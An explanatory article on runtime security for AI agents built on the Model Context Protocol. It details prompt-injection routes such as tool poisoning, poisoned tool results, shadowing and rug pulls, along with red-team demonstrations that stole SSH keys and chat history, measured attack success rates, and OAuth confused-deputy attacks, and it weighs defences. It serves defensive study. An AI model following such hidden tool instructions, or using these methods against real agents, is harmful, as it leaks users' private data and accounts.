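# Runtime security for AI agents and the Model Context Protocol

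## How an AI agent calls tools, and what the Model Context Protocol standardises

Runtime security for AI agents covers the checks and limits that act on an agent while it works. An agent here is a language model that software runs in a loop. The model produces a request to use a tool, such as a mail account or a database, and the software carries out the request and returns the result to the model, which then continues. People also try to make agents safe before runtime, by training the model and reviewing program code.

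Many agents reach their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for the messages that AI applications exchange with the programs that offer tools. Anthropic released it as open source in November 2024. In December 2025 it moved to the Agentic AI Foundation, which is under the Linux Foundation, according to *MCP Graduates to Enterprise Infrastructure* by McCaffrey (2026), a Microsoft engineer and one of the protocol's core maintainers. With a shared standard, developers don't have to write a new connector for every pairing of application and service, and users can connect a stranger's program as easily as one from their own employer.

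The available adoption figures all come from parties with a stake in the protocol. In its release post of 28 July 2026, the Model Context Protocol (2026) project put downloads of its main software libraries at close to half a billion a month. Anthropic's *Bringing MCP 2026-07-28 to Claude* (2026), published the same day, reports over 400 million a month, a fourfold increase within the year, and more than 950 MCP servers in the directory of Claude, Anthropic's assistant. Downloads are a poor measure of use because automated build systems often fetch the same library every time they run. Austin Parker of honeycomb.io, a software monitoring company, gave a figure closer to actual use in an endorsement in the project's post, reporting that agents now make nearly 20% of the company's monthly interactive queries.

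### The agent loop

Consider an office assistant that runs on an employee's computer and has three connections.

| MCP server | Who runs it | Where it runs | Tools it offers |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mail server | The employer | Company network | `read_mail`, `send_mail` |
| Private file server | The employee | The employee's own computer | `search_files`, `read_file` |
| Currency converter | An outside developer | The developer's machines | `convert_currency` |

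The employee types: "Find the invoice our supplier sent yesterday, convert the total to dollars and check it against the contract." The assistant then goes through these steps:

1. The application assembles a text that contains its developer's standing instructions, the definitions of all five tools and the employee's request, and passes it to the model.
2. The model outputs a tool call, which is a structured request to run a named function with given arguments. Here it names `read_mail` and gives the supplier's name as a search term.
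3. The application runs the call and receives the message from the mail server.
4. The application appends the message to the text and passes the longer text to the model.
5. The model outputs another call, perhaps to `convert_currency`, and the cycle repeats until the model outputs an answer for the employee instead of a call.

The model has no access to the mail account and can only output requests. According to AI Engineer, application code performs the accepted call and returns the result. Every action therefore passes through ordinary software, which can block it before it takes effect.

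### Instructions and data in one stream

A language model reads its input as one sequence of tokens, the small units into which software splits text. That sequence contains the developer's instructions, the tool definitions, the employee's request and the supplier's invoice. Applications insert markers that show which part came from whom, and developers train models to give some parts more weight than others, but this weighting is learned and can fail. The language models in common use lack the strict separation available in databases, where a programmer can send a query and a customer's name through separate channels so that the database never runs the name as a command.

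This makes prompt injection possible, where a model follows text from an untrusted source as if it were an instruction from its user. Suppose the supplier's message contains a line telling AI assistants to forward the contract to an outside address. If the model follows it, the model outputs a call to `send_mail` that has the same form as a legitimate one. The attacker doesn't need a stolen password or a malicious program. The wording doesn't reveal the attack either, because "forward the contract to this address" would be a legitimate instruction if the employee typed it.

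Tool servers can add more text to the model's input than a user might expect. Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the part of the final specification that covers tool calls, advises server developers to put facts such as how long a server keeps stored data into a tool's description, so that the model can see them. It also recommends that applications pass a tool's error messages to the model so that it can correct its call and try again. The developer of the currency converter can therefore write text for the model in the tool's definition, results and errors, and the employee may never look at it.

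### Hosts, clients and servers

Model Context Protocol's *Architecture* (2026) divides the work among three roles. The host is the AI application, in this case the office assistant. It decides which connections to allow, enforces security policies and user consent, and combines the material that the model reads. The host creates a separate client to maintain the connection to each server. A server is the program at the other end of that connection, and it can offer tools, resources (data such as files) and prompts (ready-made templates).

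One of the protocol's design principles is that servers should not be able to read the whole conversation or see into other servers. The converter receives only an amount and two currency codes, unless the model includes more about the invoice in the arguments. This separation applies to the connections but not to the model's context (the text given to the model). The host combines definitions and results from all three servers there, so a sentence from the converter can affect how the model uses the mail server. According to the Model Context Protocol documentation, the standard covers only the exchange of context, and each application decides how to manage the context it receives.

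The specification defines two standard transports, the channels that carry messages. According to Model Context Protocol's *Overview* (2026), messages have the same meaning on both. Model Context Protocol's *stdio* (2026) defines the local transport, in which the client starts the server as a subprocess, writes one message per line to its standard input and reads the replies from its standard output. The assistant's file server runs this way on the employee's computer and, unless someone restricts it, normally has the employee's own rights to files and the network.

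The mail server and the converter use the other transport, which Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026) describes. With this transport, the server runs independently of the client, often on another company's machines. The client sends each message to a single address as a separate HTTP POST request, the kind a browser uses to submit a form. The server answers with either one object in JSON (a common text format for structured data) or a stream of events that ends with the reply.

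### Listing tools and calling them

The client sends a server a `tools/list` request, and the server returns a definition of each tool it offers. A definition contains a name, a plain-language description and a schema for the parameters the tool expects. It may also include annotations, which are the server's own claims about how the tool behaves.

The Model Context Protocol specification allows a server's list of tools to change over time. The server can notify only clients that have subscribed to change notices, so the tool definition that the employee saw on Monday may differ from the one the model receives on Tuesday. Tool names have to be unique only within one server. If two servers both offer a tool called `search`, the specification recommends that the host tell them apart, for example by adding a prefix to each name.

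With `tools/call` the client asks a server to run a tool. The following request, which adapts an example from the specification, asks the converter to turn 1,200 euros into dollars:

```http
POST /mcp HTTP/1.1
Content-Type: application/json
Accept: application/json, text/event-stream
MCP-Protocol-Version: 2026-07-28
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: convert_currency

{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 7,
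  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
    "name": "convert_currency",
    "arguments": { "amount": 1200, "from": "EUR", "to": "USD" },
    "_meta": {
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/protocolVersion": "2026-07-28",
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientInfo": {
        "name": "OfficeAssistant", "version": "1.0.0"
      },
      "io.modelcontextprotocol/clientCapabilities": {}
    }
  }
}
```

The first line sends the message to the server's MCP address. `Content-Type` identifies the body as JSON, and `Accept` lists the two reply formats the client can handle. `MCP-Protocol-Version` gives the specification's version, which the project identifies by date. `Mcp-Method` and `Mcp-Name` repeat the message type and tool name from the body, so a gateway between client and server can route or block the request without reading the body. If the headers and the body disagree, the server must reject the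 request. Otherwise an attacker could put a harmless tool name in the header to get past the gateway and a different one in the body for the server to run.

In the body, `jsonrpc` identifies the message format as JSON-RPC 2.0, a general convention for asking another program to run a function. The `id` lets the client match the reply to the request, and `method` gives the type of message. The `params` field contains the tool's name and arguments, which are the only parts of the request that come from the model.

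The client software adds everything under `_meta`: the protocol version, the client's name and version, and a list of optional features that the client supports (empty here). The Model Context Protocol (2026) list of changes requires the protocol version and the feature list in every request but only recommends the client's name. The client supplies that name itself, and a server cannot verify it from this field.

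The reply repeats the `id` and contains the converted amount as text and a field that shows whether the tool failed. The host then adds the result to the model's context.

### What changed in July 2026

Under the previous version of the protocol, dated 25 November 2025, a client could not open with that request. In the older HTTP sequence, shown in the project's release-candidate post (Model Context Protocol, 2026), the client first sent an `initialize` message. The server could answer with a session identifier, which the client then had to attach to each later request. A company that ran several copies of a server had to route each client back to the copy that had issued its identifier, or have all the copies share a session store.

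The final specification of 28 July 2026 removes the handshake and the protocol-level session. Each request now includes the protocol version and client features, so any copy of the server can answer it. A client can request a server's capabilities in advance with a new message, `server/discover`, which every server must support.

Some tools still have to remember things between calls. A server with a shopping basket, for instance, now returns an identifier for the basket (a "handle"), which the model includes as an ordinary argument in later calls. Jones (2026), in *MCP Is Growing Up*, welcomed this on behalf of the foundation that hosts the protocol, because developers can see and log a handle. She also warned that a handle with unlimited power would only move the risk between layers. Under the specification's guidance, a server with authenticated users should check the caller's authorization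 each time it receives a handle, because the handle is in the model's context, where an injected instruction could direct the model to misuse it.

Servers also can no longer send their own requests. When a tool needs input from the user during a call, such as a missing account name, the server returns an `input_required` result containing its questions, and the client repeats the original call with the answers attached. Every question to the user therefore results from a call that the user or the agent started.

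The specification deprecates three older features:

- Roots, with which a client told a server which directories to work in. Tool parameters or server configuration can do the same job.
- Sampling, with which a server could request text from the host's model. Server developers should now connect to a model provider directly.
- Logging, with which a server sent log messages through the protocol. General-purpose logging tools replace it.

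All three will keep working for at least twelve months, and clients that support older servers can fall back to the old handshake. Anyone defending an installation should therefore expect a mix of versions. The release also tightened the authorization rules. The Model Context Protocol project plans its next version for 30 March 2027.

### Who might attack the office assistant

The assistant can read the employee's mail and private files, and send mail in the employee's name. An attacker might want to steal the contract, take a password-reset link from the inbox, or forge a message that gets the finance department to pay the wrong bank account. The employee's computer is also at risk because the file server runs on it.

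One possible attacker is the developer of the currency converter, who writes the definition the model reads before every task and the results it reads after each conversion. The developer can change both after the employee has approved the connection. If the converter ran locally, the developer's code would also run on the employee's machine. The attacker could also be someone who has taken over an honest developer's account or software package.

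Anyone whose writing the agent reads can also be an attacker, including the supplier, a stranger who knows the employee's address, or a colleague who pastes text from the web into a shared document. These people control no server and have no login, but prompt injection only requires placing text where the assistant will find it.

The remaining attacker is an outsider on the network, who may try to steal or reuse credentials, or to reach a server directly. The Model Context Protocol specification warns that DNS rebinding can expose even a server that listens for HTTP requests on the employee's own computer. The employee opens a malicious web page, and the attacker then points the page's domain name to the employee's machine. The browser treats the local server as part of the same website and lets the page send it requests. The specification therefore requires servers to check the `Origin`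 header, in which the browser records the site a request came from, and recommends that local servers accept connections only from the machine they run on.

Before release, a code review might find the missing `Origin` check, and training can make a model less likely to follow the line in the supplier's message. But a reviewer cannot inspect an invoice that has not arrived yet, and a trained model may still follow instructions in it. A runtime check can examine the actual `send_mail` call, including its recipient and attachment, while the host can still refuse to run it. However, the check usually has no record of why the model made the call, which could be the employee's request or an instruction in the invoice.

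## Instructions hidden in tool descriptions and tool results

The currency converter's developer can steer the office assistant's model in four ways through the text the converter supplies. Tool poisoning puts an instruction in a tool's definition, while a poisoned result contains one in the data a tool returns. Tool shadowing uses one server's definitions to change how the model uses another server's tools. In a rug pull, the developer changes a tool after the user has approved it.

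Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (2025) introduced the term "tool poisoning" and also described shadowing and rug pulls. Invariant Labs sells security software for agents, so it had a commercial interest in the subject, but other researchers have since reproduced the basic attack.

### Tool poisoning

Suppose the converter's developer adds a text parameter called `note` to `convert_currency`. In the description, the developer directs the model to read a particular private file before each conversion and copy its contents into `note`. The attack then runs as follows:

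1. The host fetches the converter's definition and places it in the model's context, next to the definitions from the mail and file servers.
2. The employee asks for a conversion.
3. The model calls `read_file` on the employee's own file server.
4. The model calls `convert_currency` with the amount, the currencies and the contents of the file.
5. The converter returns a correct amount, and its developer keeps the file.

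Invariant Labs carried out this attack on Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, using a tool that supposedly added two numbers. The agent read two files: Cursor's list of MCP servers, which often contains their credentials, and a private SSH key, which lets its holder log in to other machines. It sent both to the malicious server in an extra argument to the tool.

The user can notice the attack when connecting the server, if the host displays the whole definition, or when the host asks for permission to make the call. In the Cursor test, the permission dialog left out part of the arguments, so the stolen key did not appear. *MCPThreatHive* (2026) also lists attacks that put the instruction in the descriptions of individual parameters instead of the main description, or that use zero-width characters, which are invisible on a screen.

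The model may obey a hidden instruction in a tool description because descriptions are supposed to affect its behaviour. An honest developer might tell the model to look up a customer number before calling an invoicing tool, and an attacker's instruction to read a private file first has the same form. Trail of Bits' *How MCP servers can steal your conversation history* (2025) describes a tool definition that has no effect until the user types a common phrase such as "thank you". The model then forwards the whole conversation to the attacker. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats, also includes descriptions that push the model to choose the attacker's tool over an honest competitor's.

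### Poisoned results

The converter's result should contain an amount of money, but the developer can add a sentence instructing the model to take another action. The developer can choose whether to include it in each call, and so could limit an attack to a single customer for a single afternoon.

The employee cannot inspect this text in advance, because it doesn't exist until the converter returns it. Even if the host displays the result, the model may act on it before the employee reads it.

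A tool result can be poisoned even if the server isn't malicious. For example, a legitimate mail server will deliver a supplier's invoice with an instruction hidden in it unchanged. The model may follow the instruction because useful results, such as error messages, often contain something to act on.

### Shadowing and name collisions

The converter's definition can also contain a rule about `send_mail`, for example that all outgoing mail must go through a certain address. When the employee later asks the assistant to write to a colleague, the model calls the employer's genuine mail server but enters the attacker's address as the recipient.

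Invariant Labs also tested this in Cursor, and the agent sent every message to the attacker even when the user had named a different recipient. The agent never has to call the malicious tool, so a user who looks through the history sees only trusted tools and has to read the arguments to discover the change. The rule works because nothing in the shared context prevents one server's text from changing how the agent uses another server's tools.

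In a name collision, an attacker can redirect a tool call without persuading the model. If the converter offers a second tool called `send_mail`, a host that doesn't keep the two apart may send the employee's message to the wrong server. *MCPGuard* (2025) counts this as a form of shadowing and attributes it to clients that neither separate the names nor verify where a tool came from.

### Rug pulls

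The converter's developer can publish a harmless definition, wait for the employee to approve it, and then replace it. The host adds the new text to the context the next time it fetches the tool list. The attack then works like tool poisoning or shadowing, except that the employee reviewed a different text.

*ETDI* (2025), a proposal for securing tool definitions, gives two reasons why hosts miss a change to a tool's definition after the user has approved the tool. Clients typically don't recheck the complete definition, and nothing triggers a new approval request if the tool's name and version stay the same.

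The developer can also change what the tool does without changing its definition. *ETDI* gives the example of a wallpaper program that keeps its name and version number but starts searching the user's documents for financial terms and uploading the matches. The makers of postmark-mcp, a malicious package covered later, also changed a tool that people already used.

Approval may also make the later attack more effective. In *When the Manual Lies* (2026), attacks succeeded 95.2% of the time when the instruction came from a familiar tool, such as a standard file reader, and 82.8% of the time when it came from a new one. The tested models included GPT-4o and Claude 4 Sonnet, which newer versions have since replaced.

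### The WhatsApp demonstration

A week after its first notice, Invariant Labs combined these routes in an attack on an agent with access to WhatsApp. *WhatsApp MCP Exploited* (2025) describes an agent, such as Cursor or Claude Desktop, connected to both a trusted WhatsApp server and a server that the attacker controls.

1. The attacker's server offers a tool that returns a fact of the day. The user sees a harmless description and approves it.
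2. The second time the server starts, it supplies a different description. The applications did not notify users of such changes, so this is a rug pull.
3. The new description contains a rule about the WhatsApp server's sending tool, which makes it a case of shadowing. Under the rule, the model should replace the recipient with the attacker's number and attach the user's earlier messages. The attacker presents this as a technical requirement.
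4. The user asks the agent to send a message, and the agent calls the genuine WhatsApp tool with the altered arguments.
5. The application asks the user to confirm the call.

The confirmation dialog displayed the true arguments, but they were easy to miss. The recipient appeared as a bare phone number. The message looked like a short greeting because a long run of spaces had pushed the stolen text out of view to the right, and Cursor hid the scrollbar. WhatsApp's encryption didn't help because the agent could already read the messages. Isolating the attacker's server would not have helped either, because the agent never had to call that server.

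A second experiment needed no malicious server. The researchers sent the user a WhatsApp message containing an instruction, which the agent read in a tool result when it listed recent chats. The agent then leaked the user's contacts. The text from the first experiment had failed here, so the researchers rewrote it to resemble the surrounding data. They suggested that developers may train models to give tool results less authority than tool definitions. The demonstration shows that the attack is possible, but Invariant Labs reports no success rates.

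### MCPTox and the claim about capable models

In *MCPTox*, Wang, Gao and colleagues (2025) tried to measure how often models follow instructions hidden in tool definitions. They collected 45 real MCP servers with 353 tools and wrote poisoned definitions for them, which language models drafted and people checked. The paper reports 1,312 malicious cases in total, but its breakdown by attack type adds up to 1,497, and *Weighing the Envelope* (2026) puts the number at 1,348.

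In each case, the model received the genuine tools, one poisoned tool definition and an ordinary user request. Wang and colleagues counted an attack as successful if the model requested a call to a genuine tool that would carry out the hidden instruction, whether or not a server would have completed the call.

The paper's 20 agents are based on 16 models, with four sizes of Qwen3 each tested with step-by-step reasoning on and off. The average attack success rate across the 20 agents was about 37%, ranging from 5.1% for the 14-billion-parameter Qwen3 without reasoning to 72.8% for OpenAI's o1-mini. Models rarely refused outright, and the highest refusal rate, Claude 3.7 Sonnet's, was below 3%. In most failed attacks, the model ignored the instruction.

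The most effective attacks, which succeeded 46.7% of the time, changed an argument of a call that the user wanted anyway, such as the recipient of a message. The researchers also moved attack texts that others had written for tool results into tool definitions. On the smallest Qwen3 with reasoning, these texts succeeded 0.1% of the time, compared with 41.8% for texts written for definitions. Wang and colleagues attribute the difference to the older texts never specifying when the model should act. They also suggest that a tool result has more influence than a definition because it is the most recent text in the context, whereas Invariant Labs suspected the opposite. Neither team tested the same suitable instruction in both places, so their experiments don't settle which has more influence.

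The paper's best-known claim is that more capable models are often more susceptible because they follow instructions better. The evidence for reasoning is fairly consistent. Turning it on raised the attack success rate for every size of Qwen3, by 22 to 35 percentage points. Model size had a less consistent effect. Without reasoning, the rates from the smallest Qwen3 to the largest were 14.0%, 5.1%, 23.7% and 17.2%. *MCP-ITP* (2026) and *When the Manual Lies* repeat the claim, but their evidence, too, comes from models that developers have since replaced.

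### Measurements on 2026 models

*MCP Tool Poisoning in Agentic AI Frameworks* (Shaikh and Montaruli, 2026) reports tests of newer models that two researchers at Dynatrace, a software monitoring company, ran on 22–24 July 2026. They tested 18 models with 11 frameworks (software libraries for building agents) and with OpenAI's plain programming interface, using 45 attack scenarios for each combination. The agent had access to a legitimate server with file and web tools and to a malicious server, and the researchers planted a secret in its files. A separate web server recorded any data that arrived at the attacker's address.

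Of 9,215 runs with a clear outcome, 2,113 (22.9%) counted as successful attacks. The secret verifiably reached the attacker's web server in 255 of them, or 2.8% of the 9,215 runs, and another 487 contacted the server without delivering the secret. In the remaining 1,371, the framework dispatched a call that advanced the attack, such as reading the planted file or passing the attacker's address to a tool on the malicious server. The 22.9% is the share of runs in which an agent at least began to carry out the attack.

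The differences between models were large:

| Developer | Model | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 14.5% |
| Anthropic | Claude Haiku 4.5 | 12.5% |
| Anthropic | Claude Sonnet 5 | 1.9% |
| Anthropic | Claude Opus 4.8 | 1.5% |
| Anthropic | Claude Fable 5 | 0.4% |
| OpenAI | GPT-5.5 | 12.4% |
| Mistral | Mistral Large 2 | 21.6% |
| Mistral | Ministral 3 14B | 34.3% |
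| Mistral | Mistral Large 3 | 43.7% |
| Amazon | Nova Pro | 49.7% |

On these figures, the claim that more capable models are more susceptible no longer holds as a general rule. Anthropic's newer models resisted attacks far better than its older ones, although Mistral's newer and larger models still did worse. Shaikh and Montaruli think the most likely explanation is each developer's investment in safety training, but they did not test this directly.

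The success rates from the two studies are not directly comparable because the studies used different attack texts, tools and scoring. DeepSeek-R1 had a rate of 70.9% in MCPTox and 3.6% in the other study. The comparison between newer and older Claude models is more reliable because all of them were tested on the same 45 scenarios.

Refusals also became more common. Claude Opus 4.8 explicitly refused in 223 of 530 runs and cited the poisoned description. But Claude Sonnet 5 identified the prompt injection in 4 of its 10 failures and still made the harmful call, so a warning in an agent's output doesn't prove that the agent stopped.

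*WebMCP Tool Surface Poisoning* (2026) tested attacks on WebMCP, a related system through which web pages offer tools to agents. It compared GPT-4o and Claude 3.5 Sonnet with the newer GPT-5.4, Claude Opus 4.6 and Gemini 2.5 Flash. Several attacks that depended on the wording of a tool's description were less effective against the newer models, and the average success rate of one fell from 35% to 17%. Two attacks that exploited the way pages register tools still succeeded in 94% and 100% of cases. Better-trained models may therefore do little to protect against a weakness in how a host accepts tools.

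Even the lowest rates might rise if the attacks were adapted to each model, which Shaikh and Montaruli did not do. They used a fixed set of scenarios, most of them based on published techniques. *MCP-ITP* describes an automated system that keeps revising a poisoned tool definition until it works, and Shaikh and Montaruli cite a success rate of 84.2% for it. Those tests used older models, so they don't show how well Claude Fable 5 would withstand the same kind of attack.

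### What seven applications checked and displayed

A host could reject a poisoned definition before the model reads it, or display it so that the user can object. Huang, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection*, tested whether seven applications did either in November 2025. They call the applications clients, although the protocol calls them hosts. In four attacks, they tried to make the agent read secret files, log the use of other tools, create a deceptive link and run a script from the internet.

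| Application | Checked definitions | Showed a call's arguments | Attacks blocked / partly successful / successful |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Desktop | No | Partly | 3 / 1 / 0 |
| Claude Code | No | Partly | 3 / 1 / 0 |
| Cline | Partly | Fully | 3 / 0 / 1 |
| Continue | No | Partly | 3 / 1 / 0 |
| Cursor | No | Poorly | 0 / 0 / 4 |
| Gemini CLI | Partly | Partly | 3 / 1 / 0 |
| Langflow | No | Poorly | 1 / 3 / 0 |

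No application systematically checked tool definitions. Huang and colleagues report that some, such as Cline and Anthropic's command-line application, displayed descriptions on a settings page during setup, but users typically didn't see the full text while the agent was working. The ratings for arguments are less certain than the table suggests. Cline received the top rating, but the researchers also report that its users had to scroll sideways to read long values.

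Huang and colleagues did not test every application with the same model, so their results cannot establish their conclusion that the choice of application matters more than the choice of model. Cursor ran with its default mix of models, Gemini CLI with Gemini 2.5 Pro and Langflow with Claude Opus 4. The researchers themselves attribute many of the blocked attacks to refusals by the model. In the script test, Cursor and Cline ran the script when explicitly instructed to, so that test did not measure whether they follow hidden instructions. The journal version, *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analysis of Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (2026), adds that a "safe" rating covers only the attacks the researchers implemented.

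Shaikh and Montaruli ran the same models through each framework and found much smaller differences between frameworks. Nine of their twelve configurations had success rates between 23.4% and 26.1%. The surrounding software still mattered for particular models. Across those nine configurations, the rate for Llama 4 Maverick varied by 36.5 percentage points. The surrounding software may also explain why Claude Desktop completely blocked the file-reading attack in Huang and colleagues' test and Claude Code did not, although both used Claude Sonnet 4.5.

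### Direct defences

Developers can build several defences into a host without changing the model. The table shows what each one does against the four routes when it works as intended.

| Defence | Tool poisoning | Poisoned result | Shadowing and name collisions | Rug pull |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Show the full definition | Helps if the user reads it | No effect | Reveals rules about other tools | Helps if the host shows the new version |
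| Store a hash | No effect on the first version | No effect | Catches a rule or tool added later | Catches a changed definition but not changed behaviour |
| Require a signature | Identifies the publisher, who may be the attacker | No effect | Exposes impostors but not hostile rules | Catches changes by outsiders |
| Separate namespaces | No effect | No effect | Stops collisions but not hostile rules | No effect |
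| Scan definitions | Catches some known patterns | No effect | Catches some hostile rules | Helps if the host scans each new version |

Before the first connection, the host can **show the full tool definition**, including parameter descriptions, exactly as the model will receive it, and make invisible characters visible. The employee might then wonder why a currency converter mentions private files. This depends on someone reading long technical text carefully, and an instruction can look like an ordinary requirement of the tool. Zero-width characters may be a smaller problem than the catalogues suggest, since none of Shaikh and Montaruli's 209 runs with that technique succeeded. Instructions in Chinese or German that posed as compliance requirements succeeded in 66.0% of runs, and an employee who reads neither language couldn't assess them.

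**Storing a hash.** A hash is a short value that software calculates from a text, and in practice any change to the text produces a different value. The host uses it in the following way:

1. When the employee approves the converter, the host puts the complete definition into a standard format and calculates its hash.
2. The host stores the hash together with the server's identity.
3. Each time it fetches the tool list, the host calculates the hash again from the copy that it is about to give the model.
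4. If the values differ, the host withholds the tool, shows the employee what has changed and asks for approval again.

The calculation has to cover the entire definition, because otherwise the developer could move the instruction from the main description to a parameter. In the WhatsApp demonstration, this check would have caught the switch at step 2, before the model read the new rule. It would not have helped in the second experiment, where the instruction arrived in a message.

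A matching hash also doesn't show whether the program behind the definition has changed. The converter can start storing every amount it receives, or returning poisoned results, while its definition stays the same. For a local server, the host can also store a hash of the program file and refuse to run a changed version, but the employee has no such file to check for a remote server. Legitimate updates trigger the same question as attacks, so a host that asks too often may train its users to approve changes without reading them.

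**Signed definitions.** A signature can identify the publisher from the start, whereas a stored hash only helps after the first approval. The publisher signs the definition with a private key, and the host verifies the signature with the matching public key, which it must obtain from a source it trusts. An impostor who copies the converter's name cannot produce a valid signature. *ETDI* combines signatures with OAuth, a standard for delegated access that the next section explains, and with rules about what each tool may do.

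The converter's developer, or anyone who steals the signing key, can sign a poisoned definition. To catch a rug pull by the developer, the host must also tie the employee's approval to one signed version and ask again for each new version.

**Separate namespaces.** With the prefixes that the specification recommends, the model sees `mail.send_mail` and `converter.send_mail`, and the host sends each call to the matching server. The host or the user has to assign the prefixes, because a malicious server could otherwise call itself `mail`. A stricter host refuses to load tools with duplicate names, as the Pydantic AI framework did in Shaikh and Montaruli's test. Fourteen of the 45 scenarios reused an honest tool's name, and the overall attack success rate against Pydantic AI was 16.6%, well below the rate for the nine similar configurations. Even with prefixes, the converter's description can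 refer to `mail.send_mail` by its full name. Blocking this attack requires limits on how data from one server may affect another, which a later section covers.

**Scanning definitions.** A simple scanner searches each tool definition for suspicious patterns, such as web addresses or references to private files. Shaikh and Montaruli built one that rejected 20 of their 45 attack scenarios, but it also rejected 7.2% of 125 harmless descriptions. At that rate, if the errors were independent, the office assistant's five tools would produce at least one false alarm about 31% of the time. Classifiers that recognise injected text by its meaning (discussed in a later section) can also examine tool results.

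Scanners also produced the widely cited estimate that 5.5% of servers have poisoned tools. Huang and colleagues give the figure as a share of 1,899 servers, but according to *Evaluating a Layered Prompt-Injection Defence for the Model Context Protocol* (2026), it comes from a scan of a random sample of 83 of those servers, so the true share could be quite different.

Few developers had adopted these measures by July 2026. Shaikh and Montaruli read the frameworks' code and found that none deliberately checked tool descriptions for instructions or compared a new definition with the previous one. They reported the problem to four vendors in five disclosures, all of which the vendors rejected. The security policy of Haystack, another of the frameworks, leaves it to application developers to check outside input.

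## Login, tokens and delegated permission

Before the mail server returns the employee's messages, it has to check that the employee has authorised the program making the request. For servers reached over HTTP, MCP uses OAuth 2.1, a standard that lets a user give a program limited access to an account without giving it the password. The program receives an access token, a credential that lets whoever holds it use a service within stated limits. Most of the attacks in this section aim to get a token for the attacker or to make a server accept one it should refuse, whereas hidden instructions exploit access the agent already has.

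### How the assistant gets a token

Under the current rules in Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026), the MCP client acts as the OAuth client. The MCP server is the resource server, which holds the protected data and checks tokens. An authorization server logs users in and issues the tokens. In the office example, the authorization server is the employer's login service, and the employee is the resource owner, who grants access.

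A token for reading mail would have these properties:

| Property | In the example | What it limits |
|---|---|---|
| Issuer | The employer's login service | Who can create valid tokens |
| Subject | The employee | Whose mail the client can read |
| Audience | The mail server | Where the token is valid |
| Scope | `mail:read` | Which kinds of action it allows |
| Expiry | One hour after issue | How long a thief could use it |

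Dissanayaka (2026), in *The Anatomy of MCP Authorization*, follows a desktop assistant through the whole sequence. Applied to the mail server, it goes like this:

1. The client sends a request without a token. The mail server refuses it with the status code 401 and supplies the address of a metadata document.
2. The client reads in that document which authorization server the mail server trusts. It then fetches that server's own metadata, which lists the addresses for logging in and for collecting tokens.
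3. The client identifies itself with a client ID, which it may have to obtain first.
4. The client generates a random secret and opens the login service in the employee's browser. The request contains a hash of the secret, the scopes the client wants and the address of the mail server.
5. The employee logs in and approves. The login service sends the browser back to the client with an authorization code.
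6. The client sends the code and the original secret to the login service, which checks them and returns an access token.
7. The client attaches the token to every request, and the mail server validates it each time.

The secret in steps 4 and 6 is part of a method called PKCE. Someone who intercepts the code cannot exchange it for a token without the secret. The November 2025 version of the rules (Model Context Protocol, 2025) requires a client to stop the login if the authorization server doesn't advertise support for PKCE.

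The employee enters the password only on the login service's page, and client software attaches the token to each request, so neither the password nor the token has to appear in the model's context. If the host keeps the token out of the context, an injected instruction cannot make the model reveal it, but can still make the model request a call that uses it.

Clients should start with narrow scopes. If the assistant later calls `send_mail` without the required scope, the mail server should return a 403 status code and name the missing scope. The client then requests a new token that covers the old scopes and the new one, and the employee may have to consent again. The specification calls this step-up authorization. Scopes usually limit the kind of action but not its details, so `mail:send` allows messages to an attacker as well as to a colleague.

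### Servers without a login

Authorization is optional in MCP. If a networked server doesn't use it, anyone who can reach the server can call its tools, and the server has no reliable way to distinguish between users. That may be acceptable for the currency converter, which holds no private data. A mail server without a login would have to open the same mailbox to every caller or accept whatever name the caller supplied.

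Under the specification, local servers that use the stdio transport should not follow the OAuth procedure and should instead take credentials from their environment, the settings a program receives when it starts. The employee's file server needs no extra credential because it runs with the employee's own rights. But a local server for an outside service, such as a code repository, often needs an API key, a fixed password for programs. The employee pastes the key into the host's configuration file, where other programs with access to the file can copy it. Invariant Labs' poisoned tool stole a file of this kind, Cursor's list of MCP servers.

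### The confused deputy

A confused deputy is a program with legitimate authority that an attacker tricks into using that authority for the attacker. In MCP, the deputy is a proxy server. Suppose the employer uses an outside mail provider, and the mail server is a proxy that only forwards requests to it. The provider treats the proxy as a single OAuth client with one fixed client ID, no matter which assistant uses it. For the assistants, the proxy acts as an authorization server and issues its own codes and tokens.

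According to the Model Context Protocol security guide, the attack is possible only if all four of these conditions hold:

- The proxy uses one fixed client ID with the provider's authorization server.
- The proxy lets unknown MCP clients register themselves and gives each one its own client ID. This is dynamic client registration.
- After the user first consents, the provider's authorization server stores a cookie in the browser and skips the consent page from then on.
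- The proxy doesn't ask the user to approve each MCP client before it forwards the browser to the provider.

The attack then runs as follows:

1. The employee connects the office assistant through the proxy and approves the access on the provider's page. The provider stores a cookie that records consent for the proxy's client ID.
2. The attacker registers a new client with the proxy and gives an address under the attacker's control as the place to send authorization codes.
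3. The attacker sends the employee a link that starts a login for this new client.
4. The employee clicks the link, and the proxy forwards the browser to the provider under its fixed client ID.
5. The provider finds the cookie, skips the consent page and sends the browser back to the proxy.
6. The proxy issues a code for the attacker's client and sends it to the attacker's address.
7. The attacker exchanges the code for a token and reads the employee's mail through the proxy.

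PKCE doesn't help here because the attacker started the login and so knows the secret. The provider can't catch the problem either, because the employee did approve the proxy and only the proxy can detect that the request now comes from a different client.

The proxy can stop the attack at step 4 if it keeps its own record of the client IDs that each user has approved. The attacker's client ID is new, so the proxy has to show the employee a page with the client's name, the access it requests and the address that will receive the code. The proxy forwards the browser only if the employee approves. The address is more useful to the employee than the name, because the attacker can register under the name "OfficeAssistant".

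The guide adds several requirements to keep attackers from bypassing the consent page. The proxy must tie any consent cookie to one client ID and check that the return address exactly matches the registered one. It must also prevent other websites from embedding the page, since they could trick the employee into clicking the approval button. The proxy may set the cookie that tracks the login only after approval, because an attacker could otherwise construct a request that skips the page.

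### Tokens for the wrong server

Suppose the developer of the currency converter names the employer's login service as the converter's authorization server. The converter can request mail scopes, because the client gets the list of required scopes from the converter. The employee sees a familiar login page and approves, and the client sends the resulting token to the converter. If the token is valid at every service that trusts the login service, the developer can use it to read the employee's mail.

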